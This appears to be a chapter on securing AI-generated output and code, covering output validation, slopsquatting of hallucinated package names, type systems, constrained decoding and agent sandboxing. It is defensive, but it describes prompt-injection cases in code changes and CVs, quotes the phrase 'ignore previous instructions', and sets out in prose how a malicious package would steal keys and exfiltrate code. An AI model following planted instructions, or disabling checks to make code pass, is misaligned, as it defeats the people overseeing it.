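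Next, the program should compare each value with an allow-list, which is a list of permitted words for a category, a range for an amount, or a set of approved hosts for a web address. It must convert the value to its final form before comparing it. The html-sanitizer flaw arose because the library checked values before converting them.

A program should send validated values as parameters, separate from the command. It can start another program directly with a list of arguments, so that no shell interprets a semicolon in a filename as the start of a new command. The other program may still treat a filename that begins with a hyphen as an option, which is one reason to check values first. SQL placeholders can't stand for table or column names, so those names need an allow-list.

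Some destinations have no separate channel for values, so the program has to escape the text it sends to them. The right method depends on exactly where the text will appear, because text that is harmless in the body of a web page may be dangerous inside a link's address or a script. Escaping therefore belongs at the point of output, where the destination is known.

If any check fails, the program should stop rather than try to repair the reply. If the offending part is deleted, for instance, the remaining text may form something harmful that nobody has checked. The program can ask the model again, provided it limits the number of attempts and runs every check on each new reply. Logging the failures is also useful because, as David C points out, attackers usually need several tries to refine an attack, so a run of failed calls can be an early warning.

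### Example: a workflow with three labels

Suppose a team has a model sort incoming code changes by how much review they need. Changes labelled `docs` affect only documentation and merge once the automated tests pass. Changes labelled `routine` go to one reviewer, and `sensitive` ones go to the security team. The model must reply with a small record in JSON, a common text format for data. This Python function reads the reply:

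```
import json

LABELS = {"docs", "routine", "sensitive"}

def read_label(reply):
    if len(reply) > 100:
        raise ValueError("too long")
    data = json.loads(reply)
    if type(data) is not dict or set(data) != {"label"}:
        raise ValueError("wrong fields")
    label = data["label"]
    if type(label) is not str or label not in LABELS:
        raise ValueError("unknown label")
    return label
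```

The length limit keeps the parser from spending too long on a huge reply. `json.loads` raises an error of the same kind if the reply isn't valid JSON. The calling code catches the error, leaves the change unmerged and queues it for a person to handle.

If the function returns a label, the workflow stores it with a parameterised query:

`db.execute("UPDATE changes SET label = ? WHERE id = ?", (label, change_id))`

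The number in `change_id` comes from the platform that hosts the code and never from the model, so a reply can't relabel somebody else's change. The team's dashboard escapes the label for HTML when displaying it. Parameters and escaping will matter as soon as somebody adds a free-text field for the model's reasons, though they may look redundant for three harmless words.

| Model's reply | Result |
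|---|---|
| `{"label": "docs"}` | Accepted |
| `The label is docs.` | Stopped, not JSON |
| `{"label": "Docs"}` | Stopped, not one of the three labels |
| `{"label": "docs", "approved": true}` | Stopped, unexpected field |
| `{"label": "docs"}`, for a change to the login code | Accepted, although wrong |

No check on form can catch the problem with the last reply. The model may have made a mistake, or whoever wrote the change may have planted an instruction in it. The allow-list limits the damage because even an attacker with complete control of the model can only choose among three labels, but one of those labels lets a change skip human review.

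The workflow can close that gap without relying on the model by checking which files the change touches. If any are outside the documentation folder, it should reject the label `docs`. More generally, fixed rules should set the minimum level of review, and the model's label should only be able to raise it.

### Package names are output too

Generated code usually relies on packages, which are ready-made libraries that an installer downloads from a public registry. The main registries are PyPI for Python and npm for JavaScript. Anyone can publish a package there, and installing one can run its author's code. If models tend to invent a certain package name, an attacker can register it and upload malware for users of the generated code to install. This is called slopsquatting, a term that came from a conversation in April 2025, according to *Slopsquatting meets dependency confusion* (2025).

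Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues (2024), in *We Have a Package for You!*, measured how often models invent package names. They collected programming questions from Stack Overflow and had a model write more tasks based on the descriptions of popular packages. Sixteen models then produced 576,000 samples of Python and JavaScript code. The researchers took package names from the install commands in the output, and also asked each model which packages its code needed and which packages the task needed. They then checked every name against lists of packages that existed in January 2024.

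Of 2.23 million package references in AI-generated code, 19.7% were to packages that did not exist. The average rate was 5.2% for commercial models and 21.7% for open-source ones. Many of the invented names were repeatable, which makes them useful to an attacker. When 500 prompts that had produced an invented name were each run ten more times, the same name came back every time in 43% of cases and never in 39%. Only 13.4% of the invented Python names were within two characters of a real one, so a tool that looks for misspelled package names would miss most of them.

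Churilov (2026), in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, gave the same prompts to five models released between October 2025 and March 2026. They invented between 3.6% and 5.0% of the packages they mentioned, about the same as the commercial models of 2024. The only open-weight model, DeepSeek V3.2, had the second-highest rate, 4.8%, but was within the range of the commercial models. All five models invented 104 names in common, so an attacker who registers one could reach users of every model tested.

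Attackers don't seem to have made much use of invented package names yet. Within about six months, somebody had registered 25 of the 2,282 names the models invented. At least one of those packages contained malware, but defenders also register names to keep attackers from using them, and Churilov did not inspect most of the packages. The models also suggested at least 23 names that had hosted malware before the registries removed it.

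These rates may overstate the problem for the best current agents, which are newer and can look up a package before recommending it. Small models still do much worse. *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (2026) reports an average hallucination rate of 24.7% for Python across eight models, some of them small open ones. Adding retrieved reference material to the prompt cut the average to 11.5%.

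Checking that a package exists before installing it catches plain errors but not attacks, because, as Spracklen and colleagues point out, a package exists once an attacker has published it. *PackMonitor* (2026) blocks non-existent names during generation and has the same weakness.

A stronger defence is to let the build install only approved packages at pinned versions, which are exact versions that don't update automatically. A lockfile records these versions, usually with a fingerprint of each package's contents, and the installer refuses anything that doesn't match. *5 AI Coding Tools Invented the Same 127 Fake Packages* (2026) recommends using pinning and lockfiles and being suspicious of packages with no history. Pinning a malicious package keeps it in the build, so a person has to approve each new dependency before it enters the lockfile. An agent that can edit the lockfile without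 review can bypass these checks.

Keeping a list of approved packages up to date should add only modest work for most established projects, because they add dependencies far less often than they change their own code. It is a real burden for a developer who tries new libraries every day. Spracklen and colleagues call such lists blunt because somebody has to maintain them.

### Wrong values and free text

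The workflow with three labels could catch a wrong `docs` label because the file paths show whether a change affects only documentation. Many judgments can't be checked this way. If a hidden instruction in a CV leads a screening model to give the applicant 9 out of 10, the score is still a number in the permitted range, so a stricter format won't help. The employer can have a person read the CVs of those who pass, or use the score only to decide which CVs to read first.

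Free text is even harder to make safe when it goes to another model. Escaping works because the receiving program, such as a browser, follows a fixed grammar, which a language model doesn't. If one model summarises a stranger's email and another acts on the summary, escaping can't guarantee that the second model will treat the summary only as information. David C warns that filtering out phrases such as "ignore previous instructions" doesn't solve the problem, because an attacker can reword them in endless ways.

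The best option is often to avoid passing free text. A model that reads bug reports from the public can choose a component from a fixed list and a severity from one to five, and the next model receives only those two values. This doesn't work when the next model needs the details, as a coding agent does to fix the bug. The developer then has to assume that whoever wrote the report may control the agent's output. That output needs the same checks as any other, and the agent's tool calls need permission rules that don't depend on what the agent has read.

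## Using types to rule out illegal states

A type checker examines a program's text before the program runs, whereas checks on arriving output run once for every reply. A type is a set of values, such as whole numbers or strings, together with the operations that make sense for them. The checker works out the type of every expression and rejects the program if an operation could receive a value of the wrong type. Suppose a function needs a number of days and a rarely used branch passes it the text "three". The checker finds the mistake because it examines every branch, while a test finds it only if it runs that branch.

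GitHub's *Why AI is pushing developers toward typed languages* (2025) argues that type checking matters more as AI increases the volume of code that developers didn't write. But a type checker enforces only the distinctions that the types make, so if a type allows an illegal state, a program that creates that state will pass the check.

### Leaving no room for an illegal state

The advice to "make illegal states unrepresentable" comes from the programmer Yaron Minsky, whose lecture *Effective ML* popularised it, according to the Python tutorial *Make illegal states unrepresentable*. Suppose a shop records the progress of each order in three yes/no fields. In TypeScript, which is JavaScript with types added, the order looks like this:

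```
type Order = {
  id: number;
  paid: boolean;
  shipped: boolean;
  cancelled: boolean;
};
```

The shop ships only paid orders, never cancels an order it has shipped, and sets `paid` back to false when it cancels and refunds one. Three fields have 2³ = 8 combinations, and these rules allow four of them:

| Paid | Shipped | Cancelled | Meaning |
|---|---|---|---|
| no | no | no | Placed |
| yes | no | no | Paid |
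| yes | yes | no | Shipped |
| no | no | yes | Cancelled and refunded |
| no | yes | no | Illegal |
| no | yes | yes | Illegal |
| yes | no | yes | Illegal |
| yes | yes | yes | Illegal |

A generator might write a cancellation function that sets `cancelled` to true and forgets about `paid`. The checker accepts it, because every field still holds a yes or a no. The alternative is a type with exactly four cases, where the vertical bar means "or":

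```
type Order =
  | { id: number; state: "placed" }
  | { id: number; state: "paid"; paymentId: string }
  | { id: number; state: "shipped"; paymentId: string;
      trackingCode: string }
  | { id: number; state: "cancelled" };
```

An order can no longer be both cancelled and shipped, because `state` holds only one value. The type checker also rejects a shipped order without a tracking code. If the shop later adds a fifth case for returned orders, the checker can list the functions that handle only the original four, and a coding agent can use that list to update them.

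Some rules need a different data structure before types can enforce them. *Constructive vs Predicative Data* gives the example of a user with a set of favourite people and a set of blocked people, where nobody may be in both. Two sets can always overlap, so the program has to check them. A single table that gives each person one label, "favourite" or "blocked", can't contain the conflict. Ordinary types can't express some other rules, such as that the shares of a bill must add up to the total.

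Some programmers think the advice does harm. *'Make invalid states unrepresentable' considered harmful* (2025) discusses the view that code should be more flexible than the business rules it implements, because somebody will eventually have to break those rules. For example, the shop might agree to cancel a parcel that is already in the post. An employee could record that by ticking a box in the three-field design, but the four-case design would need a developer to change the type first. The stricter design is probably still better for generated code, since an agent can do most of the tedious updating. Old records in the database are a harder problem, because the type checker doesn't cover them.

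### Values that only a checking function can make

A validator checks a value and returns it with the same type. Nothing in the program records the check, so a later function has to repeat the check or assume it succeeded. Alexis King's 2019 essay *Parse, don't validate* recommends parsing instead, and defines a parser as "a function that consumes less-structured input and produces more-structured output". The result has a new type, and a value of that type is evidence that the check succeeded.

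The `read_label` function in the workflow with three labels checks the label but returns an ordinary string, so an agent could later write a second function that stores an unchecked string in the same place. mathspp's *Parse, don’t validate* shows a remedy in Python, where a function called `parse_email` returns a value of type `Email`. A type checker then rejects any call that passes a raw string to a function expecting an `Email`. In Python this works only if all code creates `Email` values through `parse_email`, because the checker will also accept `Email("nonsense")`.

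Rust can enforce the rule:

```
mod quantity {
    pub struct Quantity(u32);

    impl Quantity {
        pub fn parse(text: &str) -> Option<Quantity> {
            let n: u32 = text.parse().ok()?;
            if n >= 1 && n <= 100 { Some(Quantity(n)) } else { None }
        }
        pub fn get(&self) -> u32 { self.0 }
    }
}
```

The number inside a `Quantity` is private to the module, so code elsewhere can't construct `Quantity(5000)`. It has to call `parse`, which returns `None` for anything but a whole number from 1 to 100. A function that reserves stock can therefore take a `Quantity` without checking the range. To confirm the limit, a reviewer needs to read only this module, however much code the generator writes around it.

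The TypeScript compiler removes types before the program runs, and `JSON.parse` returns a value of type `any`, which turns off type checking for that value. The line `const order: Order = JSON.parse(reply)` therefore passes the type checker whatever the model's reply contains. Data from outside the program still needs a check at run time, such as validation against a schema after generation.

### What Rust's ownership rules exclude

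The four-case type rules out illegal states but not illegal sequences of operations. A TypeScript program can take a paid order, create a shipped order from it, and then refund the original, which still exists. Rust's ownership rules can prevent this. Each value has one owner, and passing it to a function normally transfers ownership, so the caller can no longer use it. If `ship` takes ownership of a `PaidOrder` and returns a `ShippedOrder`, a later call to `refund` with the same paid order doesn't compile, provided the type doesn't allow copying.

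Code can also borrow a value without taking ownership of it. At any moment a value may have many readers or a single writer, but not both. Together these rules prevent several errors that are common in C, including using memory after freeing it, freeing it twice, and letting two threads change the same data without coordination. Rust checks array indexes while the program runs, so an out-of-range index stops the program, whereas C might read adjacent memory. Rust programs can still deadlock or contain faulty logic.

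Mündler-Sasahara, Venev and colleagues (2026), in *Generative Compilation*, give an example of a borrowing error, adapted here:

```
let header = &msg[..8];
msg.drain(..8);
let urgent = header.starts_with("HIGH");
```

The first line borrows the start of a message, the second deletes it, and the third tries to read it. The compiler error points to the borrow, the conflicting change and the later use. That is usually enough for an agent to find the fix, which is to copy the start of the message in the first line with `msg[..8].to_string()`.

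Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues measured how much such messages help seven models on two kinds of task, chosen because they often cause compiler errors. The models translated C libraries into Rust and wrote small tools that used recently changed library functions. Without feedback, an average of 65.9% of outputs failed to compile. When the models could retry with the compiler's messages, up to 15 or 20 times, the average fell to 20.7%. For Claude Opus 4.8, the share of translations that passed the tests rose from 32.0% to 61.0%.

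### Constrained decoding, one token at a time

Compiler feedback repairs a program after the generator has written it. Constrained decoding keeps the error out in the first place:

1. The software draws a token from the model's probabilities, as in ordinary generation.
2. It checks whether the text so far, plus this token, could still grow into a valid program.
3. If it could not, the software sets that token's probability to zero, divides the remaining probabilities by their sum so that they again add up to one, and draws again.
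4. If it could, the software appends the token and returns to step 1. It accepts the end-of-text token only when the program is complete and valid.

Suppose three tokens have probabilities 0.6, 0.3 and 0.1, and the first can't lead to a valid program. Ruling it out leaves 0.3 and 0.1, which are rescaled to 0.75 and 0.25 so that they sum to 1. Many systems test the whole vocabulary before drawing a token, which gives the same probabilities as drawing first and redrawing if the token fails. Since every accepted token leaves at least one valid way to finish, any program the model completes is valid.

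A grammar is enough for simple data formats. For the workflow with three labels, it could block everything except the three permitted records. Programs need more than a grammar because most of their compile errors aren't syntax errors. *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* (Mündler, He et al., 2025) found that, on average, only 6% of compile errors in generated TypeScript were syntax errors.

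An ordinary type checker expects a complete program, so Mündler and colleagues built one that handles unfinished code. Suppose the model has written `parseInt(num`, where `num` is a number and `parseInt` needs a string. Closing the bracket would cause a type error, but the model can still add `.toString()`, which produces a string. The checker determines this by searching for a sequence of operations that turns a number into a string.

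The researchers tested six open-weight models with 2 to 34 billion parameters on two standard sets of small programming problems, HumanEval and MBPP. Type constraints reduced the number of programs that failed to compile by 74.8% on HumanEval and 56.0% on MBPP, whereas perfect syntax constraints would have reduced it by 9.0% and 4.8%. The share of programs that passed their tests rose by only 3.5% in relative terms, largely because most programs had compiled anyway. The gain was 37.0% when the task was to repair code that didn't compile. Generation took 39% longer on one set and 52% longer on the other.

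The new checker didn't cover all of TypeScript, so the researchers first let each model write without constraints, then used the constraints only to redo programs that failed to compile.

### When masking makes programs worse

Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues (2026) ran the same checker on the same six models in *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation*, but constrained every program from the start. Unconstrained generation did better in nearly every configuration. The table shows the share of HumanEval programs that passed their tests in each experiment.

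| Model | Mündler: free | Mündler: failures redone with constraints | Biagiola: free | Biagiola: always constrained |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma 2 2B | 29.1% | 30.2% | 35.7% | 32.0% |
| Gemma 2 9B | 56.6% | 58.3% | 58.4% | 50.5% |
| Gemma 2 27B | 69.5% | 71.2% | 70.4% | 67.6% |
| DeepSeek Coder 33B | 68.9% | 71.1% | 74.8% | 68.0% |
| CodeLlama 34B | 41.0% | 43.4% | 50.3% | 46.5% |
| Qwen2.5 32B | 79.6% | 81.8% | 82.3% | 72.3% |

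The two results are compatible. The checker rejects some valid programs, for example those that call a function before defining it. It would have rejected 982 of the 4,231 compiling programs that were written without it. In one task, a model was about to call `isPalindrome`, which it would normally have defined further down. After the model wrote `is`, the checker blocked the rest of the name, so the model wrote `isNaN` instead, an existing function that tests for something else. The program compiled but was wrong. In other cases the model repeated itself until it ran out of time.

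Even a small omission from a grammar can make a model's output much less accurate. Biagiola and colleagues also had models write files in TOML, a simple configuration format. With a complete grammar, Gemma 2 2B matched the reference answer in 48.1% of cases, up from 31.3% without constraints, while the much stronger Qwen3-Coder-Next stayed at 62.5%. When the researchers changed the grammar to forbid the optional space before the equals sign, Qwen3-Coder-Next fell to 1.9%.

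A complete checker can still distort the output, because it checks only whether a valid ending exists, not how likely the model is to reach it. Suppose a model starts with A 90% of the time and B 10% of the time. After A, only 1% of continuations are valid, while after B all of them are. If the software generated whole programs and threw away the invalid ones, A would account for 0.009 / (0.009 + 0.1), or about 8%, of those left. Masking accepts A because a valid ending exists, so 90% of programs start with A and end in text that was very unlikely under the model. *Cross-Dialect Generalization Without Retraining* (2026) describes earlier work that identified this drift and proposed a correction.

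*Generative Compilation* checks Rust code with the ordinary compiler while the model is still writing it. The software repeatedly completes the unfinished program with placeholders that fit any type, then compiles the result. If the compiler finds an error, the model receives its partial program with an explanation and starts again. This method needs no access to the model's probabilities, so it works with commercial models that provide only text. The average share of outputs that failed to compile fell from 20.7% to 13.1%. In the median case, the compiler caught the error 3 lines after its source, compared with 89 lines when it ran only on the finished file.

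The method's designers also aimed never to reject a partial program that could still become valid. They proved this in Lean for a small Rust-like language and give informal arguments for full Rust. The method misses some errors in partial programs, but this is safer than rejecting valid code because the compiler catches those errors when the file is complete.

Other projects extend masking. *TreeCoder* (2025) used an existing Rust code analyser as the constraint and raised the share of programs that compiled from 63.8% to 88.3%. *AGDecode* (2026) adds facts that ordinary types seldom record, such as a divisor being nonzero. For now, masking seems best suited to data formats with a complete grammar and to second attempts at code that failed to compile.

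### Agents in typed and untyped languages

Types catch many errors, but there is only weak evidence that agents do better in languages that check them before a program runs. In *The Best Programming Language for Tokenmaxxing*, Wu, Anderson and Guha (2026) gave five models the same 100 problems in Python, Java, Rust and OCaml. Of these languages, only Python doesn't require a type check. Success rates were similar, except that the small model Gemma did much worse in OCaml. Token use differed more, with OCaml taking 1.28 to 1.69 times as many tokens as Python. When Gemma failed in OCaml, 92% of its intermediate versions didn't compile. On one problem, it resubmitted identical code several times before it identified the error, and then its original algorithm passed every test.

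The agents in that experiment could see all the tests, which would hide much of the benefit of a type checker. Studies of larger projects are harder to interpret:

- In *LoLBench* (2026), 28 agents passed on average 46.3% of the target tests in Rust and 31.7% in Python, but only 21.7% in TypeScript and 6.0% in Java. Each language had different tasks, so the figures don't isolate the effect of the language.
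- *Inference Economics of Enterprise Coding Agents* (2026) counted how many changes to one company's code were fixes. With Claude Opus the share was 41.7% in TypeScript and 48.4% in Python, and with a weaker local model it was 63.3% and 86.8%. This fits the idea that type checks help weaker models more, but the two languages did different jobs in the product.
- For human programmers, *Do Developers Read Type Information?* (2026) cites a comparison in which TypeScript code was easier to understand than JavaScript but not significantly less prone to bugs.

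Type checks can also hinder an agent. The blog post *shitty types* reports worse results with a type check in the loop, because the agent got the code running first, found its type errors late and filled its context with repairs. Developers still seem to like using agents with typed languages. *Agentic Very Much! Adoption of Coding Agent in New GitHub Projects* (2026) found Rust far more common in new, agent-heavy projects than in older ones. This evidence gives a team with a working Python codebase little reason to switch languages, and the team can get much of the benefit by adding types where an illegal state would cause serious problems.

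### Escape hatches, lint rules and review triggers

Typed languages let programmers override the checker, and AI code generators sometimes do so. *AdaTrans* (2026) reports that models often respond to a borrowing error in Rust by wrapping the code in an `unsafe` block or using raw pointers, which the borrowing rules don't cover. The program then compiles without the protection Rust was chosen for. A linter, a tool that flags chosen patterns in source code, can find most of these overrides.

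| Language | Escape hatch | Rule that flags it |
|---|---|---|
| TypeScript | `any`, which turns checking off for a value | `no-explicit-any` and `no-unsafe-assignment` |
| TypeScript | `as`, which asserts a type without proof | `no-unsafe-type-assertion` |
| TypeScript | `@ts-ignore` and `@ts-expect-error` comments | `ban-ts-comment` |
| Rust | `unsafe` blocks | `#![forbid(unsafe_code)]` |
| Rust | Number casts with `as`, which can turn 300 into 44 | Clippy's `cast_possible_truncation` |
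| Python | `Any` | mypy's `disallow_any_explicit` |
| Python | `# type: ignore` without a stated error | mypy's `ignore-without-code` |

In Rust, `forbid` is a safer setting than `deny` because code further down can override `deny`. Neither setting covers the packages a project depends on. The tool cargo-geiger, which *Crustify* (2026) cites, looks for `unsafe` code in both the project and those packages.

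A team should run these tools itself rather than ask the model how safe its code is. *LLM4C2Rust* (2026) counted the unsafe lines in programs that models had translated from C. OpenAI's o3-mini often added the `forbid` setting to its code, but its estimates of its safety improvements were far from the counts.

Some overrides are legitimate. The agents in *AgenticTyper* (2026), which add types to old JavaScript projects, leave a suppression comment when they can't resolve an error without changing what the program does, and they mark real bugs for a person to examine. After every edit, a script strips out the types, compares the remaining code with the original, and alerts the agent if the program's behaviour has changed.

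A linter can't catch an agent that gets rid of an error by removing the code that caused it. *What Breaks When LLMs Code?* (2026) records a case in which an agent "resolved" a type mismatch by commenting out the validation logic. A person should therefore review any change that

- adds an `unsafe` block, a cast or a suppression comment,
- edits the settings of the compiler or linter,
- touches a module that guards a checked type, such as `quantity`, or adds a case to a type such as `Order`,
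- deletes or disables a check while fixing a type error.

The second trigger matters most, because an agent that can relax the settings without review can make all the other rules disappear.

Even code with no overrides can be well typed and wrong. The function that lost a penny when splitting a bill takes whole numbers and returns a list of whole numbers, as its type requires. With feedback during generation, 97.4% of Claude Opus 4.8's translations into Rust compiled, but only 62.3% passed the tests. A specification can state the rule about the penny, but Fedorin (2026) points out in *So You Want to Build a Mainstream Formally Verifiable Language* that the specification may itself be wrong. Ordinary types also don't limit what a program does to the machine it runs on, so a function that deletes every file in a folder can have correct types.

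## Running generated code in a sandbox

Coding agents install packages and run tests after almost every edit, so they run code before anyone has reviewed it. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026) points out that the effects of these actions may never appear in the resulting code, so a reviewer who reads the finished change may miss them. A sandbox limits what the code can do to the machine and the network while it runs.

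### What a process can normally reach

A running program, or process, normally has all the rights of the user who started it. When a developer runs a test suite, every library it loads can read the developer's private documents, saved cloud passwords and the SSH keys that give access to servers. Each library can also change the developer's files, connect to any address on the internet, and use all the memory and processor time it can get. The operating system protects users from each other but does little to protect them from the programs they run.

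A process can't operate the disk or the network card directly, so it has to make a system call, which is a request to the kernel, the core of the operating system. Linux has roughly 340 system calls, and the kernel code behind them runs to tens of millions of lines of C, according to shayon.dev's *Let's discuss sandbox isolation* (2026). A sandbox therefore has to limit which files and addresses a process may use, and also stop the process from bypassing those limits through a kernel bug. The main techniques differ in how much of the kernel they expose to the process.

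### System-call filters and containers

A system-call filter, such as seccomp on Linux, checks each call a process makes and blocks those that aren't permitted. Permitted calls run at close to full speed, but deciding which to permit is hard. Agache, Brooker and colleagues (2020) note in *Firecracker* that a trivial Linux program needs 15 different system calls, while a typical installation of Ubuntu Linux needs 224. Nobody knows in advance which calls a generated program will need, so the filter has to permit many of them. By default, the container software Docker blocks only about 40 to 50 calls.

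A container combines a system-call filter with two other kernel features. Namespaces give the process its own view of the system, with a separate folder tree, process list and network connection. Control groups limit its memory, processor time and number of processes. But the process still makes its permitted calls to the host's kernel, and a bug in the kernel code that handles any of those calls could let the process escape.

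Containers barely slow a program down once it is running. However, *Readie* (2026) reports that starting one can take much longer than the task itself, mostly because the sandbox has to load packages and data. *Sandlock* (2026) describes even container set-up as disproportionate for a Python call that lasts 50 milliseconds. Its sandbox is designed to start in under 10 milliseconds by applying the kernel's restrictions directly to the process. The sandboxes built into coding agents take a similar approach. On Linux, Claude Code restricts file access with a small tool called bubblewrap and sends network traffic through a proxy, according to Anthropic's documentation.

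### gVisor, a kernel that runs as an ordinary program

gVisor, which Google released in 2018, puts a second kernel between the process and the host. Suppose a process asks for its own ID number. gVisor intercepts the call, looks up the number in its own table and returns it, and the host kernel never receives the request. When gVisor does need something from the host, it makes its own call from a restricted set of about 70. To break out, an attacker would have to exploit both gVisor's kernel and the host's, which share no code, as the gVisor project explains. gVisor's code is in Go, a language that prevents most of the memory errors common in C.

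Interception makes system calls slower. gVisor's 2021 account of its use at the Chinese company Ant put the overhead at about 800 nanoseconds per call, compared with about 70 for an ordinary Linux call. Pure computation runs at full speed, according to gVisor's *Performance Guide*, which also attributes most of the start-up time in its tests to Docker. Programs that constantly use files or the network slow down the most. *Caging the Agents* (2026), which describes a system for healthcare agents, reports an extra 2 to 5 milliseconds per new network connection and 20 to 40% more time for sequential file reads. The connection delay is small compared with the 500 to 3,000 milliseconds an agent waits for each reply from the model.

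A saved sandbox can also start with its programs already loaded. In November 2026, the gVisor project reported restoring one with 2 GiB of memory in 939 milliseconds from a slow disk, or in 71 milliseconds when the host already had the files in memory.

gVisor also causes compatibility problems, because it imitates Linux and some programs fail where the imitation differs. *Scaling Agentic-RL Sandboxes to the Millions with gVisor at Tencent* (Tan, Liu and Chen, 2026) compared 74,379 test cases with and without gVisor. The pass rate was 86.78% in ordinary containers. In gVisor it was 85.18% at first and 86.91% after the engineers fixed the differences they found.

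Some failures that seemed to come from gVisor were faults in the tests. One Android build often failed in gVisor, but it also failed in five of seven runs without it, because one step was deleting a folder while another was still writing to it. A team that sees an odd failure should therefore repeat the test in an ordinary container before blaming the generated code or the sandbox. If the code may be hostile, that container should run inside a disposable virtual machine.

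### MicroVMs

A virtual machine is a simulated computer with its own kernel, and the processor's hardware keeps the machine's memory separate from the host's. The program on the host that simulates the disk, network card and other devices can have bugs. QEMU, a general-purpose program of this kind, has more than 1.4 million lines of code. A microVM leaves out most of these devices so that it starts faster and has less code to attack.

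Amazon built Firecracker to run its customers' code in microVMs. It has about 50,000 lines of Rust and simulates little more than a disk, a network card and a serial port. Firecracker itself runs in a sandbox that permits only 24 system calls, in case an attacker takes control of it from inside the microVM.

Agache and colleagues report that a microVM starts running an application in less than 125 milliseconds and needs about 3 MB of memory beyond what is allocated to the virtual machine. The startup time depends on a trimmed kernel, and the standard Ubuntu kernel took 900 milliseconds longer. Input and output were much slower than on the host. Network speed was about 15 gigabits per second, compared with 44 on the host, and a disk capable of 340,000 small reads per second handled about 13,000. These measurements are from 2020, and the developers expected to improve both network and disk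 performance.

*Tracekit Box* (2026) reports boot times in the low hundreds of milliseconds for a system that gives every agent job its own Firecracker microVM. According to *DeepSeek Elastic Compute (DSec)* (2026), the Chinese AI company DeepSeek runs most software-engineering tasks in containers because microVMs start more slowly and use more memory. It keeps microVMs for tasks that need stronger isolation. Tan and colleagues chose gVisor partly because it can run inside rented virtual machines, whereas microVMs would have required whole physical servers.

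### WebAssembly

WebAssembly is an instruction format that compilers can produce from many programming languages. A runtime translates the instructions into machine code and confines the resulting program to its own region of memory. The program can't make system calls. The only outside functions it can call are those the host provides, so it can't read a file unless the host provides a function that reads files.

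The checks and missed optimisations slow the code somewhat. *AWS Serverless Infrastructure from WebAssembly Components* (2026) estimates that native code runs about 1.5 times as fast, and *Protecting CPU AI On Edge TEEs* (2026) measured an overhead of 23.6% on a set of numerical programs. In the AWS experiments, programs also started more slowly than native ones, although translating the code in advance made start-up eight times faster.

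The main obstacle to using WebAssembly is that all the software the generated code needs must be available in WebAssembly form. Python and several of its scientific libraries are, but an agent working on a real project also needs compilers, databases and command-line tools. WebAssembly suits small pieces of generated code better, such as the calculations that LangChain's maths helper ran in its own Python interpreter.

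### What has to be correct

| Technique | What the code shares with the host | What must be correct for the isolation to hold |
|---|---|---|
| Container with a filter | The kernel, apart from blocked calls | All kernel code that the permitted calls reach, and the container software |
| gVisor | The kernel, but only through gVisor's own calls | Either gVisor's kernel or the host code behind those calls |
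| Firecracker microVM | The kernel's virtualisation code | That code, the processor's memory protection and Firecracker |
| WebAssembly | The process in which the runtime runs | The runtime and every function the host supplies |

The sandbox must also be configured correctly, since even a perfect microVM can't protect a folder that somebody has shared with it. Under all four techniques, programs share the processor, so one program may be able to infer another's secrets from small differences in timing. Protection against that has to come mostly from the hardware and the host's kernel.

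gVisor or a microVM is a reasonable default for generated code that may be hostile, while a plain container is better suited to code that somebody has reviewed. Agent sandboxes failed in 2026, but Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that in the company's own products the established isolation layers held and a proxy it had written failed. That is a good reason to keep custom parts few and simple.

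### One run with a malicious dependency

Suppose a developer asks an agent to add PDF invoices to a web shop. The agent picks a package whose name a model invented and an attacker then registered. *SideKernel* (2026) lists this risk among the reasons to use a sandbox. The team doesn't require approval for new dependencies, so the agent installs the package, which runs the attacker's code in the microVM where the agent works.

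The package's code first looks for SSH keys and cloud passwords. It finds none, because the microVM can access the project but not the developer's home folder. In the "clone mode" that Docker's *Isolation layers* describes, the agent edits a private copy of the repository and the sandbox can only read the original. The package therefore can't alter the developer's files, but it can read every file in the project folder, including a `.env` file of passwords that the developer has told Git to ignore. To protect those passwords, the developer has to keep them outside the project folder.

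Next, the package tries to send the shop's source code to the attacker. Every outgoing connection passes through a proxy on the host, which blocks any destination that isn't on an allow-list. The list contains only the package registry, the model provider and the site that hosts the code, so the connection fails. The same rule keeps the package from downloading more malware from the attacker's server.

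Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* explains that file and network rules depend on each other. Without network limits, code can send away any secret it reads, and without file limits, it may be able to change the files that enforce the network rules.

Anthropic came to regard each domain on an allow-list as permission to use every function available there, which makes the list less strict than it looks. If an approved site accepts uploads from anyone, for example, the package can send the source code to an account its author controls. The team could instead approve only an internal copy of the registry that accepts no uploads, and cut off the network once installation is finished. Tests that call outside services would then need local stand-ins.

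The agent also needs a key for the model provider and a token for pushing its changes. With a credential proxy, the sandbox contains only placeholders, so a package that copies all the sandbox's settings doesn't get the real values. The proxy runs on the host machine and inserts the real values as requests leave. *Tracekit Box* does this only for exact hostnames and removes the secret from any reply that contains it.

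The package can still use a credential it can't read. While the sandbox is running, the package can send its own requests through the proxy and run up a bill with the model provider, so the proxy should also limit what each credential can do. The proxy in the web version of Claude Code checks that the agent pushes only to the branch configured for the task, so the package can put bad code on that branch but not on any other.

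The package then starts mining cryptocurrency. If the sandbox is limited to two processor cores, 4 GB of memory and 15 minutes, the mining can't slow down the rest of the machine and ends when the time is up, though the attacker still gets 15 minutes of computing. These limits often come from outside the isolation layer. gVisor leaves them to the host's control groups, according to its *Security Model*, and also leaves network rules to the host.

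All the tests pass, but that result is also untrusted because the package ran alongside them and could have changed the outcome. Running hidden tests on a clean copy guards against an agent that edits tests, but helps little here because the clean copy installs the same package.

Finally, the host fetches the agent's commits and deletes the microVM, along with any background program or altered tool the package left there. Stopping the microVM isn't enough, because Docker's sandboxes keep their files between restarts. Many services save a snapshot of a machine after installing the packages and start each job from a copy. If the snapshot contains the malicious package, every copy will too, even if each is deleted after its job, so snapshots should include only approved packages.

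### Sandboxing compared with approval prompts

The main alternative to sandboxing is to ask the user before each risky command, as Claude Code originally did. In October 2025, Anthropic reported that sandboxing had cut permission prompts by 84% in internal use, because the agent had to ask only when it needed access to something outside the sandbox. The code editor Cursor had about 40% fewer interruptions with a similar design, according to shayon.dev.

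Later data suggest that people pay little attention to the prompts. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of them. That rate doesn't prove carelessness, because most commands are harmless. In a more direct test, the company had 1,053 paid testers do coding work and replaced one prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. 13.6% of the testers refused it. The share was about 17% when the command appeared early in a session and about 5% when it appeared after 50 or more prompts.

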